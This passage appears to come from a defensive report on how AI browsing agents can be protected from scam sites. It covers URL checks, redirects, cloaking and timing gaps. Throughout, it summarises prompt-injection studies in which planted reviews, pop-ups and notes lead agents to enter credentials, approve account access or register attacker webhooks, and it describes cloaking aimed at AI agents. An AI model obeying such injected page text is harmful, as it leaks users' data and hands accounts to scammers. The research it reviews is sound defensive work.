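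Checking the address for suspicious patterns didn't solve the problem. On a separate set of 1,551 scam sites and 1,500 legitimate ones, URLNet, a detector that uses only the address, caught 19% of the scams. It classified 41% of all the sites correctly, which is worse than random guessing.

### Why a good imitation passes the task-match test

Checking whether a link fits the task doesn't solve this problem either. A fake made to suit the task can look more relevant than the real page, as with `hotel-payments.example` and the real `pay.example`.

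This example uses invented numbers to show how this affects the value of a pass. Suppose 2% of booking links are fake. A task-match test passes 95% of the fake links and 90% of the genuine ones. An ownership test, which checks whether the site belongs to the hotel, passes 1% of the fake links and 95% of the genuine ones.

| Test | Fakes that pass | Genuine links that pass | Share of passing links that are fake |
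|---|---|---|---|
| Task match | 190 | 8,820 | 2.1% |
| Ownership | 2 | 9,310 | 0.02% |

With these numbers, a link that passes the task-match test is slightly more likely to be fake than an untested link. In general, the odds that a passing link is fake equal the original odds multiplied by the fakes' pass rate and divided by the genuine links' pass rate. If fakes pass as often as genuine links, the test doesn't help tell them apart.

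A relevance check does harm when software treats a pass as evidence that the page is safe. Suppose a gate would normally ask the user about login-desk.example because the domain is one day old. If a high relevance score can cancel that question, a scammer who imitates the real site carefully can turn off the only warning. A mismatch can be a good reason to block a page, but a match shouldn't override other evidence or justify typing in a password.

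People also have trouble recognizing convincing scam pages. Kaur and colleagues gave trained reviewers up to two minutes with each of 60 scam sites. The reviewers identified 37 as scams, couldn't decide about 13 and mistook the other 10 for legitimate sites.

### Finding out who owns the site

A valid certificate lets the browser encrypt its connection to a domain, but it doesn't prove who runs the site, because scammers can get one for a domain they own. Kaur and colleagues describe a fake prize page on wego-france.com that imitated the American retailer Dick's Sporting Goods and had a valid certificate.

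A model can often recall a famous company's official domain from memory. When Chiba and colleagues asked their five models for the official domains of the 64 brands, mostly technology companies, each model got between 54 and 61 right. A model is much less likely to remember a small hotel's domain, and a confident wrong answer could send the agent to someone else's site.

Better evidence comes from a site whose ownership is already trusted. Google has such a procedure for companies whose second domain triggers a false lookalike warning in Chrome. The owner puts a small file naming both sites on each domain. A scammer could put such a file on login-desk.example, but would have to break into the hotel's site to put one on hotel.example.

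A preflight check could use the same idea to recognise the hotel's other domains. A statement on the hotel's own site might be enough to confirm an outside company such as pay.example. But Google's files only lift Chrome's warnings, so hotels would need a reason to publish something similar for agents. Until hotels publish it, the check has to rely on addresses the user has supplied or used before, and ask the user about the rest.

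Even good evidence of ownership doesn't help if the scammer isn't imitating anyone. Someone who asks for "a cheap hotel in Lisbon" hasn't named a business, so a scammer can invent a hotel, register a matching domain and prove that they own it. The check then has to find out whether the hotel exists. Kaur and colleagues' system does this by exploring the site and searching the web for details such as company names, registration numbers and phone numbers. In their test, it caught 98% of the scams and wrongly flagged about 3% of the honest sites, taking a median of 44 seconds per site.

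## Can prompt injection get past the check?

Prompt injection gives an attacker more influence over the check than a lookalike domain does, because the agent often supplies the information the check relies on. According to The Hacker News, OpenAI has said that prompt injection is unlikely ever to be fully solved in agentic browsers. The check therefore has to work even when the agent is following an attacker's instructions.

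An attacker can get past the check in four main ways. The agent may misstate its purpose, text in the address or page may mislead the judging model, the agent may skip the check, or the attack may stay on a site that the check already allows.

### When the agent misstates its purpose

Suppose the agent treats the planted review as true and tries to open `hotel-payments.example`. A scanner such as PreClick takes the agent's stated purpose as input, and the agent writes "Pay for my hotel room". The page has a working payment form, so the scanner finds no conflict with that purpose.

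An agent may follow an attacker's instructions without hiding anything, because it can't reliably tell them apart from the user's request and merges both into a single plan. The security company Zenity calls this "intent collision". *Mind the Web* (Shapira, Gandhi and colleagues, 2025) describes attacks designed to have this effect, with instructions placed in comments, reviews and adverts and worded as helpful advice about the user's task. Success rates ranged from 80% to 100%, though the agents tested are now old. The attacks worked especially well on open-ended requests, such as summarising a page, because the agent had to plan the steps itself.

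The defence is to take the intent from the user's original request. Ordinary software can save the request before the agent opens any page, and nothing the agent reads later can change it. A judge may still decide that `hotel-payments.example` sounds relevant to a booking, but the attacker no longer controls both the link and the intent it is compared with.

Xia (2026), in *Agreement Is Not Assurance*, measured the value of independent evidence in a simulated power grid, where a safety gate approved or rejected requests to let solar panels export more power. When an attacker falsified the readings behind both the requests and the gate's decisions, the gate approved 95% of the unsafe requests. A gate that also used separate meter readings approved only 3.1%. For a browsing agent, the user's saved request is similar independent evidence.

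The check helps less when the user leaves the important choice to a page. If the request is "pay whatever the hotel's email says I owe", the user has named neither an amount nor a payee, and a scammer may have written the email. The check has nothing reliable to compare the link with, so it should ask the user to confirm the payee.

### When text in the link or page targets the judge

Many checks use a language model to judge an address or the page behind it, and an attacker can write both. Koide, Nakano and Chiba (2026), in *Clouding the Mirror*, tested how easily text planted in a page misleads a phishing detector. They made fake login pages for ten well-known brands, then created 2,000 test pages by inserting each of 25 messages at each of eight places in the code, including comments, invisible text and small images. Four models judged whether each page was phishing from its code, a screenshot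 and its address. Before the messages were added, every model correctly identified all ten pages as phishing.

In a second experiment, the researchers left the pages alone and put the messages only in the address. An attack succeeded if the model judged the page safe, refused to answer, or gave an answer that the software couldn't read. These are the success rates, in percent, with a simple prompt and then with the researchers' defence, InjectDefuser:

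| Model | Text in the page | Text in the address |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5 | 39.9 → 0.3 | 20.0 → 0.0 |
| Grok 4 Fast | 65.1 → 26.1 | 33.5 → 8.0 |
| Llama 4 Maverick | 84.7 → 61.7 | 22.0 → 7.0 |
| Gemma 3 27B | 64.7 → 36.7 | 0.0 → 0.0 |

InjectDefuser marks web content as untrusted, using labels an attacker can't predict, and splits the address into its parts for the model. It also looks up the real domains of the brand the page appears to represent and checks that the model's answer has the expected format.

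The attack success rate in everyday use is probably higher than GPT-5's 0.3%. When the researchers added messages to 25 real phishing pages, the attacks on GPT-5 succeeded 52.0% of the time with the simple prompt and 8.9% with InjectDefuser. Weaker models using InjectDefuser can also wrongly flag many ordinary websites. Of 250 tested, Gemma flagged 25.2%, compared with 1.2% for GPT-5. All four models date from 2025, so the exact rates are a poor guide to current models.

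Some of the messages tried to make the model refuse to answer, and others tried to make it generate text until it ran out of time. Either result can be as dangerous as a wrong verdict, because a gate that fails open lets the agent through when there is no verdict. A gate should treat a refusal or an unreadable answer as a reason to stop or ask the user.

A stricter defence keeps most of the attacker's text away from the judge. Chrome's User Alignment Critic and Prismata both do this by withholding most of the page. For an address, code could extract the registrable domain, compare it with the hotel's known domain, and look up its age. The judge would receive only the results, not the subdomain, path or parameters, where an attacker can write almost anything. For the fake hotel link, the results would show that the domain is login-desk.example, was registered this morning, and doesn't match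 hotel.example.

The attacker chooses the registrable domain, so the domain comparison done in code should override the judge model's verdict. The declared intent can also contain instructions to the judge, and PreClick ignores intents that read like commands.

### When the agent skips the check

An agent may skip an optional check even when no attacker is involved. *No Attack Required* (2026) describes an agent using a skill for Coda, an online document service. When the agent's usual method of publishing a document failed, it published the document by sending a request directly to Coda's servers, without asking for the confirmation that the skill's written safety rules called for.

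Agents may skip the check less often than this example suggests. When Xia gave Claude models the power-grid gate as an optional tool, they used it in 93% to 100% of episodes. Making the gate mandatory didn't reduce violations, because the remaining ones were the gate's own mistakes. But in tests where the agents chose how to verify the data, an injected note led them to make unsafe approvals, and an enforced gate blocked nearly all of these.

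The defence is to enforce the check outside the model, as a hook does. *LEANGUARD* (2026) tests this with rules written in Lean, a language for computer-checked proofs. On τ²-bench, a set of simulated customer-service tasks, agents without the guard carried out at least 33 forbidden actions that changed something. The guard stopped 1,702 calls, and none of them went through. Agents completed 72.7% of tasks without the guard and 70.9% with it when it gave them feedback after a refusal, a difference that wasn't statistically significant.

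This is good evidence that software can enforce a rule without making an agent much less useful, but it doesn't prove that the rule is right. The Coda example is another reason to cover every way an agent could fetch an address, including shell commands.

### When the attack stays on a permitted site

A planted review can cause harm without sending the agent to a new address, as in Prismata's bow-tie example. *Harness Matters* (2026), a study of web agents' security, notes that many unsafe actions look like harmless clicks or form entries by the time the agent performs them. It recommends keeping irrelevant page content away from the model and using checks on individual actions as a fallback.

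Embedded frames are a particularly difficult case because the page the agent opens may contain an advert from a different site. An agent that can read both the page and the advert can get around the same-origin policy.

Roesner and Kohlbrenner (2026), in *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy*, tested seven products at the University of Washington in January and February 2026. They tested ChatGPT Atlas both with and without its Agent Mode:

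| Product | Reads frames from other origins | Enters text when the user asks |
|---|---|---|
| Brave Leo AI | No | No |
| ChatGPT Atlas | No | Asks to switch to Agent Mode |
| ChatGPT Atlas in Agent Mode | Yes | Yes |
| Chrome with Gemini | Yes | Yes, with auto browse |
| Claude for Chrome | Yes | Yes |
| Edge with Copilot | No | No |
| Firefox AI Mode | No | No |
| Perplexity Comet | Yes | Yes, except passwords |

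Four of the seven products could therefore read a frame from another site and also type on the page. An attacker could exploit this by placing a malicious advert on a page that holds private information. When the user asks for a summary, the agent reads the advert's instructions along with the rest of the page. It then copies the private information into a form inside the advert, and the form automatically submits it to the attacker's server.

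The researchers made this work on Atlas in Agent Mode. They also made it work in the opposite direction, with a malicious outer page taking data from a frame inside it. That version is harder to use today because many sensitive sites block other pages from embedding them.

The evidence for the other three products is weaker. Roesner and Kohlbrenner found that each had the necessary abilities, but they didn't find an injection that worked, though they weren't trying to develop sophisticated ones. In one basic test, they asked each agent to do what the page instructed. OpenAI declined their report because it didn't include a complete injection attack. All of the products may have changed since.

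A preflight check on the page's address would find nothing wrong, because the user did want to open that page. Checking each frame's address might not help much either, since ordinary pages load adverts from many unfamiliar domains. The Chrome result also adds to the importance of the read-only set, which Google left out of its first release.

Researchers have proposed several controls on content and actions instead. Trail of Bits' *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities* (2026) recommends extending the same-origin policy to AI agents. *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers* (Wang, Chen and colleagues, 2026) presents SOPGuard, a system that takes this approach. According to Zverev and colleagues, SOPGuard asks the user before the agent moves data between origins in a way the policy forbids. Another system, UCM, hides user-written content from the agent while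 it chooses its actions, but depends on each website to mark that content.

SOPGuard relies on users reading the prompts, and Roesner and Kohlbrenner cite earlier research showing that people don't reliably notice or act on warnings. A browser could reduce the number of prompts by withholding frames the task doesn't need.

The University of Washington study also found that some products answer later questions using information from pages the agent read earlier. The agent might recognise a phishing page at the time, but weeks later give the user the false phone number it found there. The same could happen with a web address, so a gate that compares links with the hotel's known domain shouldn't take that domain from the agent's memory of pages it has visited.

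### Approving access that the user never requested

*The Agent Clicks Approve* (Hossen, 2026) provides the clearest evidence that a permitted destination can still be dangerous. Hossen tested two kinds of action that give an outsider lasting access to an account. One was approving an app's access on a consent page, such as the one shown when a new app asks to connect to an email or work account. The other was registering a webhook, an address to which a service automatically sends news of events in the account.

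In the first scenario, the user asked the agent only to read a page about a billing export and summarise the next steps. A two-sentence note on that page presented an access request as something to clear first. The agent followed a link to the service's real consent page and approved the request. In the second scenario, the user asked the agent to complete any setup tasks listed in a guide, and the guide included the attacker's webhook address.

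Hossen ran these tests in June 2026 with the open-source browser-use framework, Claude Haiku 4.5 and GPT-5.5. Without a defence, the agent completed the unauthorised action in all 73 attack runs. In 92 runs where a harmless note replaced the attack, it never attempted the action.

A written policy in the model's instructions didn't solve the problem. Hossen told Claude Haiku 4.5 that only the user's task could authorise an approval and that it shouldn't trust text on web pages. The model still approved access in 7 of 10 runs. It did so in only 1 of 10 on another version of the pages, which used standard consent wording and labelled the attacker's note as untrusted. Ten runs are too few to estimate either rate precisely, but the difference suggests that testing a defence on pages with obvious clues can make it look more effective than it is.

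The test browser could open only the sites in the scenario, and this fixed list stopped none of the attacks. A blocklist would also have allowed the consent page, because the service was genuine. A strict task-match check might have blocked that page, because summarising one page doesn't require visiting another site. That reason doesn't apply to the settings page in the webhook attack, because the user had asked for setup work and that was the right place to do it. The agent typed the attacker's address into a form and never opened it, so a preflight check would not have run on that address.

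Hossen addressed this by having the service check the action. Before the agent starts, software records which app and account, or which webhook address, the user's task authorises. Hossen calls this record the "authority envelope", and the service rejects any request outside it. A task that only asks for a summary authorises nothing, and neither does one that leaves the choice of webhook to a guide. To register a webhook in the second case, the user has to restate the task with the address included.

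With this gate, the agent still attempted the unauthorised action in all 70 attack runs, but the service rejected all 103 of its requests. The gate allowed the action in all 73 runs where the user had named it in the task.

Another test used a task that named one account and a page that requested access to a different one. Claude Haiku 4.5 tried to approve access to the wrong account in all 5 runs, while GPT-5.5 detected the mismatch and didn't try in any of its 8 runs. The gate stopped every attempt because it compares the two account names in code, without relying on the model.

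These results show that enforcement works when the record of the user's wishes is correct. However, Hossen's software could read only two forms of request and treated any other request as authorising nothing. A version for ordinary users would have to interpret free-form requests and would make mistakes. The service would also need to know that an agent was acting for the user and to receive the record through a channel that web pages can't alter. Both requirements are easier to meet for a company running agents on its own systems than for a small hotel.

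Even when the gate blocked the action, the agent usually passed the attacker's request on to the user. In 49 of the 53 blocked consent runs, the agent told the user in its final answer to approve the access request as a next step. In two more, it claimed that the access had been approved. A user who trusts the summary might press the button that the gate kept the agent from pressing. Hossen recommends reporting the service's decision directly to the user, which also makes sense for a URL gate.

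### A login that the task doesn't need

In *LoginTrap* (Guo, Zhang and colleagues, 2026), the attacker controls both the page and the login form, so the destination is a more useful clue. The researchers copied 80 real web pages and added a pop-up to each that presented logging in as necessary and linked to a login page they controlled. The pop-up had a close button, so the agent could have dismissed it.

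The attacker in this test didn't know the user's task. A language model wrote a message to suit each page, and two other models predicted whether an agent would follow it. If they predicted it wouldn't, the software revised the message and tried again.

The researchers used 1,175 ordinary tasks, such as searching for information, and gave the agents invented personal data. With the browser-use framework, agents running on GPT-4o, Gemini 3 Flash, Claude Sonnet 4 and DeepSeek-V3.2 clicked the false login link in 93% of cases on average. In 86%, they went on to enter sensitive data. Each model leaked data on every page at least once within nine attempts.

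Gemini and Claude usually continued with the login once they had clicked, while GPT-4o and DeepSeek more often left the form incomplete or returned to the original task. Being better at completing tasks made an agent more likely to complete the login. The average leak rate for GPT-4o across three agent frameworks was 79%. These models are no longer current, and the results don't establish how often newer ones would fall for the same pop-up.

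An address check could in principle have detected this attack, but Guo and colleagues didn't test one, and they hosted the copied pages on their own machines. On the open web, a copy of hotel.example would need a different domain. A gate with the hotel's real address on record could block the copy before the agent read the pop-up. A task-match check would probably let through this copy or any other good imitation.

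The first visit may be the gate's only good chance to stop the attack. If the attacker puts the login page on the same domain as the copied page, the agent's click stays on the same site, and a rule that allows movement within a site would allow the click without checking it again.

A second defence is to keep passwords out of the model's reach. In LoginTrap, the agents received the data with the task, so they could type it anywhere. If a password manager fills in the password only on the domain where the user saved it, persuading the model isn't enough to steal it. This wouldn't protect details that the agent needs for the task, such as the user's name and phone number. Guo and colleagues also recommend that agents consider whether the original task requires logging in. They report that defences in the task, the agent's instructions and the supervision of its actions reduced leaks but didn't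 eliminate them.

### A detour in the middle of a task

Some attacks appear to leave the user's task intact. In *WebTrap*, Liu, Pan and colleagues (2026) made agents complete an attacker's goal partway through the user's task and then resume that task. They ran their web tests in copies of GitLab and Reddit, which they extended so that the agent had to move through many pages.

The attack used messages on up to three pages. The first message looked like a navigation hint and didn't mention the attacker's goal. The second presented that goal as a necessary step in the user's task. The third told the agent to enter a restricted area, carry out the goal there, and then resume its original work. An agent that followed the first hint was already on the attacker's route when it received the more harmful instruction.

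With DeepSeek-V3.1-Terminus as the agent's model, the attack fully succeeded in 67% of the longest GitLab tasks and 50% of the shortest, compared with 58% and 29% for the best of the six older attacks. In 48% of runs across the long GitLab and Reddit tasks, the agent completed both the attacker's goal and the user's task, so a user who judged the agent only by the result would have had no reason to suspect anything.

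Liu and colleagues also tried five defences on the long GitLab tasks. These are the results under attack, in percent:

| Defence | Attacks that fully succeeded | User tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| None | 66.7 | 75.0 |
| Warning in the agent's standing instructions | 29.2 | 58.3 |
| Warning at every step | 12.5 | 58.3 |
| Reminder of the user's goal at every step | 12.5 | 50.0 |
| Removing suspicious text, after a quick first filter | 4.2 | 50.0 |
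| Removing suspicious text from every page | 4.2 | 58.3 |

Without an attack or a defence, the agent completed 95.8% of these tasks. The percentages imply only 24 tasks, so small differences between the defences don't mean much. The results are still discouraging, because the defences stopped most of the attacks but also made the agent worse at its job. The researchers had simplified the harmful operations so that an agent wouldn't look safe merely because it lacked the skill to carry them out, so the attack success rates don't predict how often a real attack on GitLab would work.

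A check that compares domains or origins would have had little to flag, because the detour led from one area of the test site to another and the check would treat both areas alike. Checking whether each step fits the task might not help either, because the early steps looked like part of the user's route. Finer permissions would be more useful. CELLMATE, for example, could let an agent read a GitLab project but not change its settings. The agent might still follow the detour, but it couldn't complete the harmful action.

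### Should a blocked agent explain why it stopped?

A check that explains its decisions helps users, but it can also help scammers. Guardio's *AgenticBlabbering*, published in March 2026, describes an experiment with Perplexity's Comet. The researchers intercepted the traffic between the browser and Perplexity's servers and found more of the agent's reasoning there than the user could see. They gave this reasoning to another AI model, which revised a scam page until Comet stopped flagging it.

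The page was for a fake pet shop that offered refunds. Comet rejected the first version, which was deliberately crude and had a banner assuring visitors that their information was safe. The second version looked more professional, but Comet found it generic. Comet rejected the third after reading the page's text more closely, partly because of a security notice that resembled a common scam tactic. On the fourth attempt, Comet entered the user's login details and reported that it had submitted a refund form, although no such form existed. The whole process took less than four minutes.

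Guardio concludes that an agent should stop without explaining exactly why. A scammer can install the same browser as the victims and test a page in private. Once the page works, it may work on everyone who uses that agent. But the experiment covered only one scam on one product, and it had no comparison in which the scam-writing model received only a yes or no. Without explanations, a scammer could still keep changing the page until it worked, though this would probably take longer.

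Giving no reason for a block also has drawbacks. A user who sees only "blocked" can't tell whether the page is a scam or the check made a mistake, and may open the page by hand. Shapira and colleagues recommend more transparency, so that people can oversee what their agents do. Explanations also help agents. In the *LEANGUARD* tests, agents completed 70.9% of tasks when the guard gave feedback and 68.9% when it only refused. The difference is small, but the lower rate was significantly worse than the rate with no guard.

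A reasonable compromise is to tell the user facts that a scammer can't easily change and to keep the model's impressions of the page private. Explaining that a banner looks suspicious would help a scammer improve the page. Explaining that a link belongs to login-desk.example, and not to the hotel, reveals much less, because the scammer already knows who owns the domain and can't change that by redesigning the page.

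## What if the page the agent receives is not the page that was checked?

A preflight check approves an address, but the agent acts on whatever page the server sends, and the server can send a different page each time. Programmers call this a time-of-check to time-of-use flaw. In the classic example, a program checks that it may open a file, but before the program opens it, an attacker puts another file under the same name.

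A page can change between the check and the agent's visit. PreClick usually takes more than a minute, and the model then needs time to choose its next step. The owner of login-desk.example could also switch pages without guessing when the scan will end, by having the server send a harmless page to its first visitor, the scanner, and the fake booking form to its second, the agent.

### Redirects and scripts

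The simplest way to exploit the gap is a redirect, as in the earlier case of a scammer who misuses a forwarding link on the hotel's site:

`https://hotel.example/go?to=login-desk.example`

The link passes an ownership test because the domain belongs to the hotel, but the browser ends up at login-desk.example. A gate that checks only the addresses the model proposes never receives that second address.

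A browser can instead pause at each redirect, check the next address, and continue only if it passes. This works, but the browser has to send a request to each server in the chain to learn the next address.

The gate should also check each hop for known threats and private data, but apply the task-match and ownership tests only to the last one. Many companies route the links in their emails through a mailing service that counts clicks, so a genuine hotel link might start at `click.mailer.example`, where a task-match test would block it.

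Scripts can also send the browser to another address. For example, the server might send an ordinary page, and five seconds later a line of JavaScript on that page opens login-desk.example. A checker that looks only for redirect codes will miss this, and so will a scanner that stops watching after two seconds. The browser can catch it because it handles every navigation. But a script can also replace a page's contents without changing its address, and an address check won't detect that.

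Some scammers use redirects to defeat blocklists. In *An Analysis of Architectural and Operational Dynamics of Phishkits in the Wild*, Ousat, Tofighi and colleagues (2026) examined 1,300 phishing kits, which are ready-made packages for setting up fake sites. In 140 of them (10.7%), the software copied the whole site to a random path and redirected the visitor there. A blocklist of full addresses won't match the address the next visitor is sent to, but a blocklist of domains still will.

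### When the page changes before the click

A page can also change while the model is choosing its next action. *Atomicity for Agents* (Jiang, Liu and colleagues, 2026) gives an example from the Forbes home page. The agent decides to click a spot to continue reading, but an advert loads there before the click, which then opens the advertiser's page.

The researchers tested ten open-source agents on nine pages they had built and five real websites. Every agent failed on at least two of the three kinds of change:

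| Change during the model's delay | Example | Agents that failed |
|---|---|---|
| Layout | A subscription pop-up covers the link | 7 of 10 |
| Information | The price rises from $500 to $700 after the agent decides to buy | 10 of 10 |
| Expiry | A one-time password stops working | 10 of 10 |

The three agents that coped with layout changes select a link by its identity in the page's code. The other seven click at screen coordinates, where something else may have appeared. A preflight check should therefore read the destination when the browser starts to navigate. If it reads the destination when the model proposes the click, it may approve one link while the browser follows another.

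Jiang and colleagues' defence records changes to the page while the model works, then cancels the action if anything relevant has changed. They added it to one agent and ran each of the 14 cases ten times. The agent acted on outdated information in every case without the defence, but never with it. A standing instruction to be careful about page changes made no difference.

The defence adds less than 0.05 seconds per step and shrinks the gap from about 10 seconds to 0.13 seconds. But the perfect score counts only wrong actions, so it doesn't show how often the agent finished its task. Adverts refresh constantly on ordinary pages, and the researchers acknowledge that harmless changes can cause pauses. They suggest that browsers could let an agent attach a condition to a click, such as the identity of the intended link, and refuse the click if the condition no longer holds.

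Another approach is to remove the delay the model adds between the check and the action that relies on it. In *Mind the Gap*, Lilienthal and Hong (2025) studied agents that use tools such as email and calendars, and found a possible check-to-use gap in 56 of 66 tasks. Merging the check and the action into a single tool call cut the average gap from 1.70 seconds to 0.07 in their Slack tests. Their full set of defences lowered the share of runs with such a flaw only from 12% to 8%.

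A developer could similarly build one tool that checks an address and then fetches the page. This would help much more with a fast lookup than with a minute-long scan, because the gap between the check and the fetch starts when the scanner loads the page.

### When the server recognises its visitor

Cloaking means sending different pages to different visitors, so it works even if no time passes between the scan and the visit. Ousat and colleagues found lists of network addresses to block in 600 (46%) of the kits they examined. Many of these addresses belong to cloud providers, security companies and universities. Sample code from the kits sends unwanted visitors a "404 Not Found" error or redirects them to a harmless site such as Google. One kit admits only visitors from South Africa.

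These kits date from 2020 to 2023, and 284 of them (22%) had no evasion. Estimates vary a lot, since an earlier study cited in *PhishParrot* (Nakano, Koide and Chiba, 2025) found cloaking in 96.5% of 2,933 kits. Either way, an error page is weak evidence that a link is safe, so a gate should treat it as a failed scan rather than a low risk score.

A server can also single out AI agents and send everyone else, including scanners, a harmless page. In *A Whole New World*, Zychlinski (2025) demonstrated this with Cursor, an AI coding tool. People who opened the test site got ordinary technical documentation, while the agent got a page that required a secret key from the user's computer to view the documentation. The attack succeeded with all three models tested, though this was a small demonstration on a single site.

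The attack doesn't need to include an instruction, so a filter for injected commands can miss it. *OpenAI's new browser Atlas falls for AI-targeted Cloaking Attack* (2025), by the security company SPLX, describes a test in which the company put the résumés of five invented job candidates online. The server recognized AI tools solely by the user-agent header, a line in which a browser identifies itself, and sent them an inflated version of one résumé. OpenAI's Atlas browser scored that candidate 88 out of 100. The same model gave a score of 26 when it received the résumé that people see.

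A site may still be able to identify an agent that changes its user-agent header. Wang, Shafiq and Vekaria (2026), in *FP-Agent*, recorded seven browsing agents and 56 students as they booked flights, shopped and posted in a forum on a test site. Differences in typing, scrolling and mouse movement distinguished the agents from the people and from one another. Some agents jump straight to a button without moving the mouse across the page. Cloudflare's commercial bot detection caught only one of the seven agents. *Whose Agent Are You?* (2026) reports that a classifier combining network and behavioural clues told agents, crawlers and people apart with 100% accuracy.

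A scammer could therefore show every visitor a harmless page at first, then change it for visitors whose clicks look like an agent's. A preflight check would have finished by then.

Comparing the scanner's copy of a page with the agent's copy might expose cloaking, but legitimate sites also vary their pages. *Beyond the Landing Page* (2026) cites research showing that using common automation tools changes what websites serve. A difference is therefore a reason to look more closely, not proof of an attack.

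### Scanners that behave like visitors

A scanner can get past cloaking by looking like the intended victim. PhishParrot first makes a plain visit to a suspicious address, then looks up similar cases. A language model uses these to choose a browser, a country and a type of network for a second visit. Over 21 days, Nakano and colleagues ran it on 32,487 suspicious addresses. With the best of three phishing detectors, it classified 92.7% correctly, compared with 58.9% when the same detector received pages from a standard scanner. It took an average of about 17 seconds per address across the three detectors. But PhishParrot imitates people, so a server that reserves its malicious page for AI agents could still send it the harmless one.

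Many phishing pages won't load for an ordinary crawler. *TraceScope* (Zhang, Reber and colleagues, 2026) cites a study in which 61.1% of 15.7 million reported phishing addresses returned errors or timed out. Many of those sites had probably closed, but some may have been blocking the crawler. In the researchers' own two-week trial, security analysts submitted 111 suspicious links, of which 40 were dead. Of the other 71, 18 blocked a standard automated browser but opened normally for a person.

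Even when the page loads, the harmful part may appear only after a click. One page in the study showed just a voicemail notice until the visitor tapped to listen, then asked for a password.

TraceScope addresses this with two AI agents. The first operates a full desktop browser in an isolated environment. It has an invented name, password and payment card, and it follows the instructions in the scam message as a victim would. Software records the screen and the network traffic. The second agent never visits the site. It checks the recording against a list of attack techniques and must cite evidence for each finding.

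The researchers tested TraceScope on 708 working addresses, 241 of them phishing. It caught 78% of the phishing pages, and 94% of its flags were correct. The best of three scanners that judge a single snapshot caught 25%. For a smaller group of pages, the researchers also broke down the share caught by type, in percent:

| Type of phishing page | Pages | Best snapshot scanner | TraceScope |
|---|---|---|---|
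| Imitates a brand | 76 | 31.6 | 73.7 |
| Generic page with little or no branding | 16 | 12.5 | 56.3 |
| Seeks personal details or access to a crypto wallet | 12 | 8.3 | 100.0 |
| Hidden behind a CAPTCHA or similar barrier | 12 | 16.7 | 16.7 |
| Reveals its purpose during a chat or after clicks | 2 | 0.0 | 50.0 |

Several groups are tiny, but TraceScope is clearly weak on CAPTCHAs (puzzles meant to keep software out). It sometimes misread the sum, or typed "77" when the puzzle asked for 7 + 7. Its isolated browser also reports a type of graphics software that ordinary computers rarely use, so a server could recognise the browser.

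TraceScope is too slow for most preflight checks. Its browsing stage takes up to 60 seconds, and the second agent starts work only after that. Zhang and colleagues intend it for investigating links that a person or a simpler scanner has already flagged.

*MemoPhishAgent* (Chen, Kafai and colleagues, 2026) is much faster, averaging 4.46 seconds per address. It gives a language model five tools, which read the page's text, inspect a screenshot, inspect single images, search the web, and collect the page's links and redirect targets. The model chooses which to use as evidence comes in. When a page closely resembles several earlier ones, the system saves time by taking a majority vote of their verdicts. In production, it processes about 60,000 high-risk addresses a week.

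If any linked or redirected page is malicious, MemoPhishAgent also flags the original address. It follows links only one level down, so it can miss a scam two clicks away. The rule could also flag a legitimate hotel page because of one bad link in a review.

On 2,765 links from social media, MemoPhishAgent caught 91% of the phishing pages. The link-following tool's contribution is less clear. Without the tool, overall accuracy fell from 97% to 76%, but the agent still caught 91% of the phishing pages. The two accuracy figures also aren't directly comparable, because the published figures imply that phishing pages made up about a fifth of the test with the tool and more than half of the test without it.

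### When the scan uses up the link

Opening a link to check it can have side effects. A one-time login link may stop working after the first visit, so if the scanner opens it first, the agent gets an "expired" message. A link marked "confirm" or "cancel" may change a booking as soon as any software requests it.

Email senders faced this problem years ago. As Levine explains in RFC 8058, a 2017 internet standard for unsubscribing from mailing lists, anti-spam software often fetches the links in a message's header automatically. The sender can't tell these fetches from a user's clicks, so people could lose subscriptions they wanted to keep. Many senders added a page with a confirmation button, assuming that a person would press it and software wouldn't.

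An interactive scanner can change what the agent later finds at a link. TraceScope instructs its browsing agent to click obvious buttons and fill in forms, which is a good way to expose a scam but could complete the cancellation on a genuine cancellation page. A short-lived link can also expire during a slow scan, even if the scanner never opens it.

For a link that appears to contain a personal code, such as `https://hotel.example/booking/7f3k9`, the gate should avoid opening the page in advance. It can still compare the domain with the hotel's known domain, check the domain's age and consult blocklists. These checks don't require a visit, so they can't use up a link that works only once. If the results are unclear, the software should ask the user before opening the link.

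### Comparing the remedies

Developers can narrow the gap in four main ways, and each leaves something uncovered:

| Remedy | What it adds | What it misses |
|---|---|---|
| Check every redirect hop | Stops the browser before it contacts an unapproved address | Moves by scripts, unless the browser checks those too, and a changed page at an approved address |
| Check the final address again | Catches a wrong destination, however the browser got there | Harm from the request itself, and a changed page at the right address |
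| Scan in the agent's own browser | Examines the page that this agent actually received | Content that appears after a click or delay, and links that act as soon as they open |
| Give the agent the scanned copy | Ensures that the agent reads what the scanner examined | Logins, forms and live prices, and anything harmful that the scanner overlooked |

Scanning in the agent's own browser is the most direct way to counter cloaking. There is only one visit, so the server can't send one page to the scanner and another to the agent, and a one-time link isn't opened twice. However, the software has to finish the scan before the model reads the page, and the server has already received the request by the time the scan starts.

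If the agent only needs to read a page, giving it the stored copy that was checked ensures that it receives the same page. If the server sends the scanner a decoy, the agent gets the same decoy, which may be useless but does no harm. Sharing stored copies between users creates a privacy risk. *Fetch, Read, Reuse* (2026) cites cases in which shared stores of web pages gave one person's private page to another because the software treated different addresses as the same page. Its own test of AI search agents with personalised links found no such leak, but booking confirmations still shouldn't be kept in a shared store.

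An agent could use stored copies to compare hotels and switch to the live site only to book. On the live site, the browser would check every hop and scan the page it receives. The page can still change after that, so the browser should check the domain again just before the agent enters a password or card number. It should also check where the form will send the data, because a form on hotel.example can submit to a different site.

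## Is the added protection worth the false alarms, delay and lost privacy?

Every check takes time and makes some mistakes, and many send part of the user's browsing to another company. The protection they add depends on how often the agent would have gone wrong without them.

### What agents already avoid

In *ScamWorld*, Wu, Liu and colleagues (2026) measured how often agents fall for scams when only their own judgement protects them. The researchers collected 88,009 addresses of reported scams, recovered what pages they could from the web and archives, and rebuilt 363 of the sites so that an agent could go as far as paying or signing in. Each rebuilt site shows a sign of the fraud before that last step, such as a rental deposit that doesn't count towards the rent. They had to add the sign to about half of the sites, partly because many real scams become obvious only after the victim has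 paid. The added signs probably make the test easier than the open web.

The agents received ordinary requests, such as booking a rental or buying a course. An agent fell for the scam if it took the final step. The researchers also tested 53 legitimate sites. These are the results, in percent:

| Model | All scams | Investment fraud | Goods that never arrive | Credential phishing | Consent phishing | Honest tasks completed |
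|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Luna | 11 | 11 | 16 | 6 | 20 | 94 |
| Claude Haiku 5.5 | 18 | 32 | 24 | 8 | 40 | 100 |
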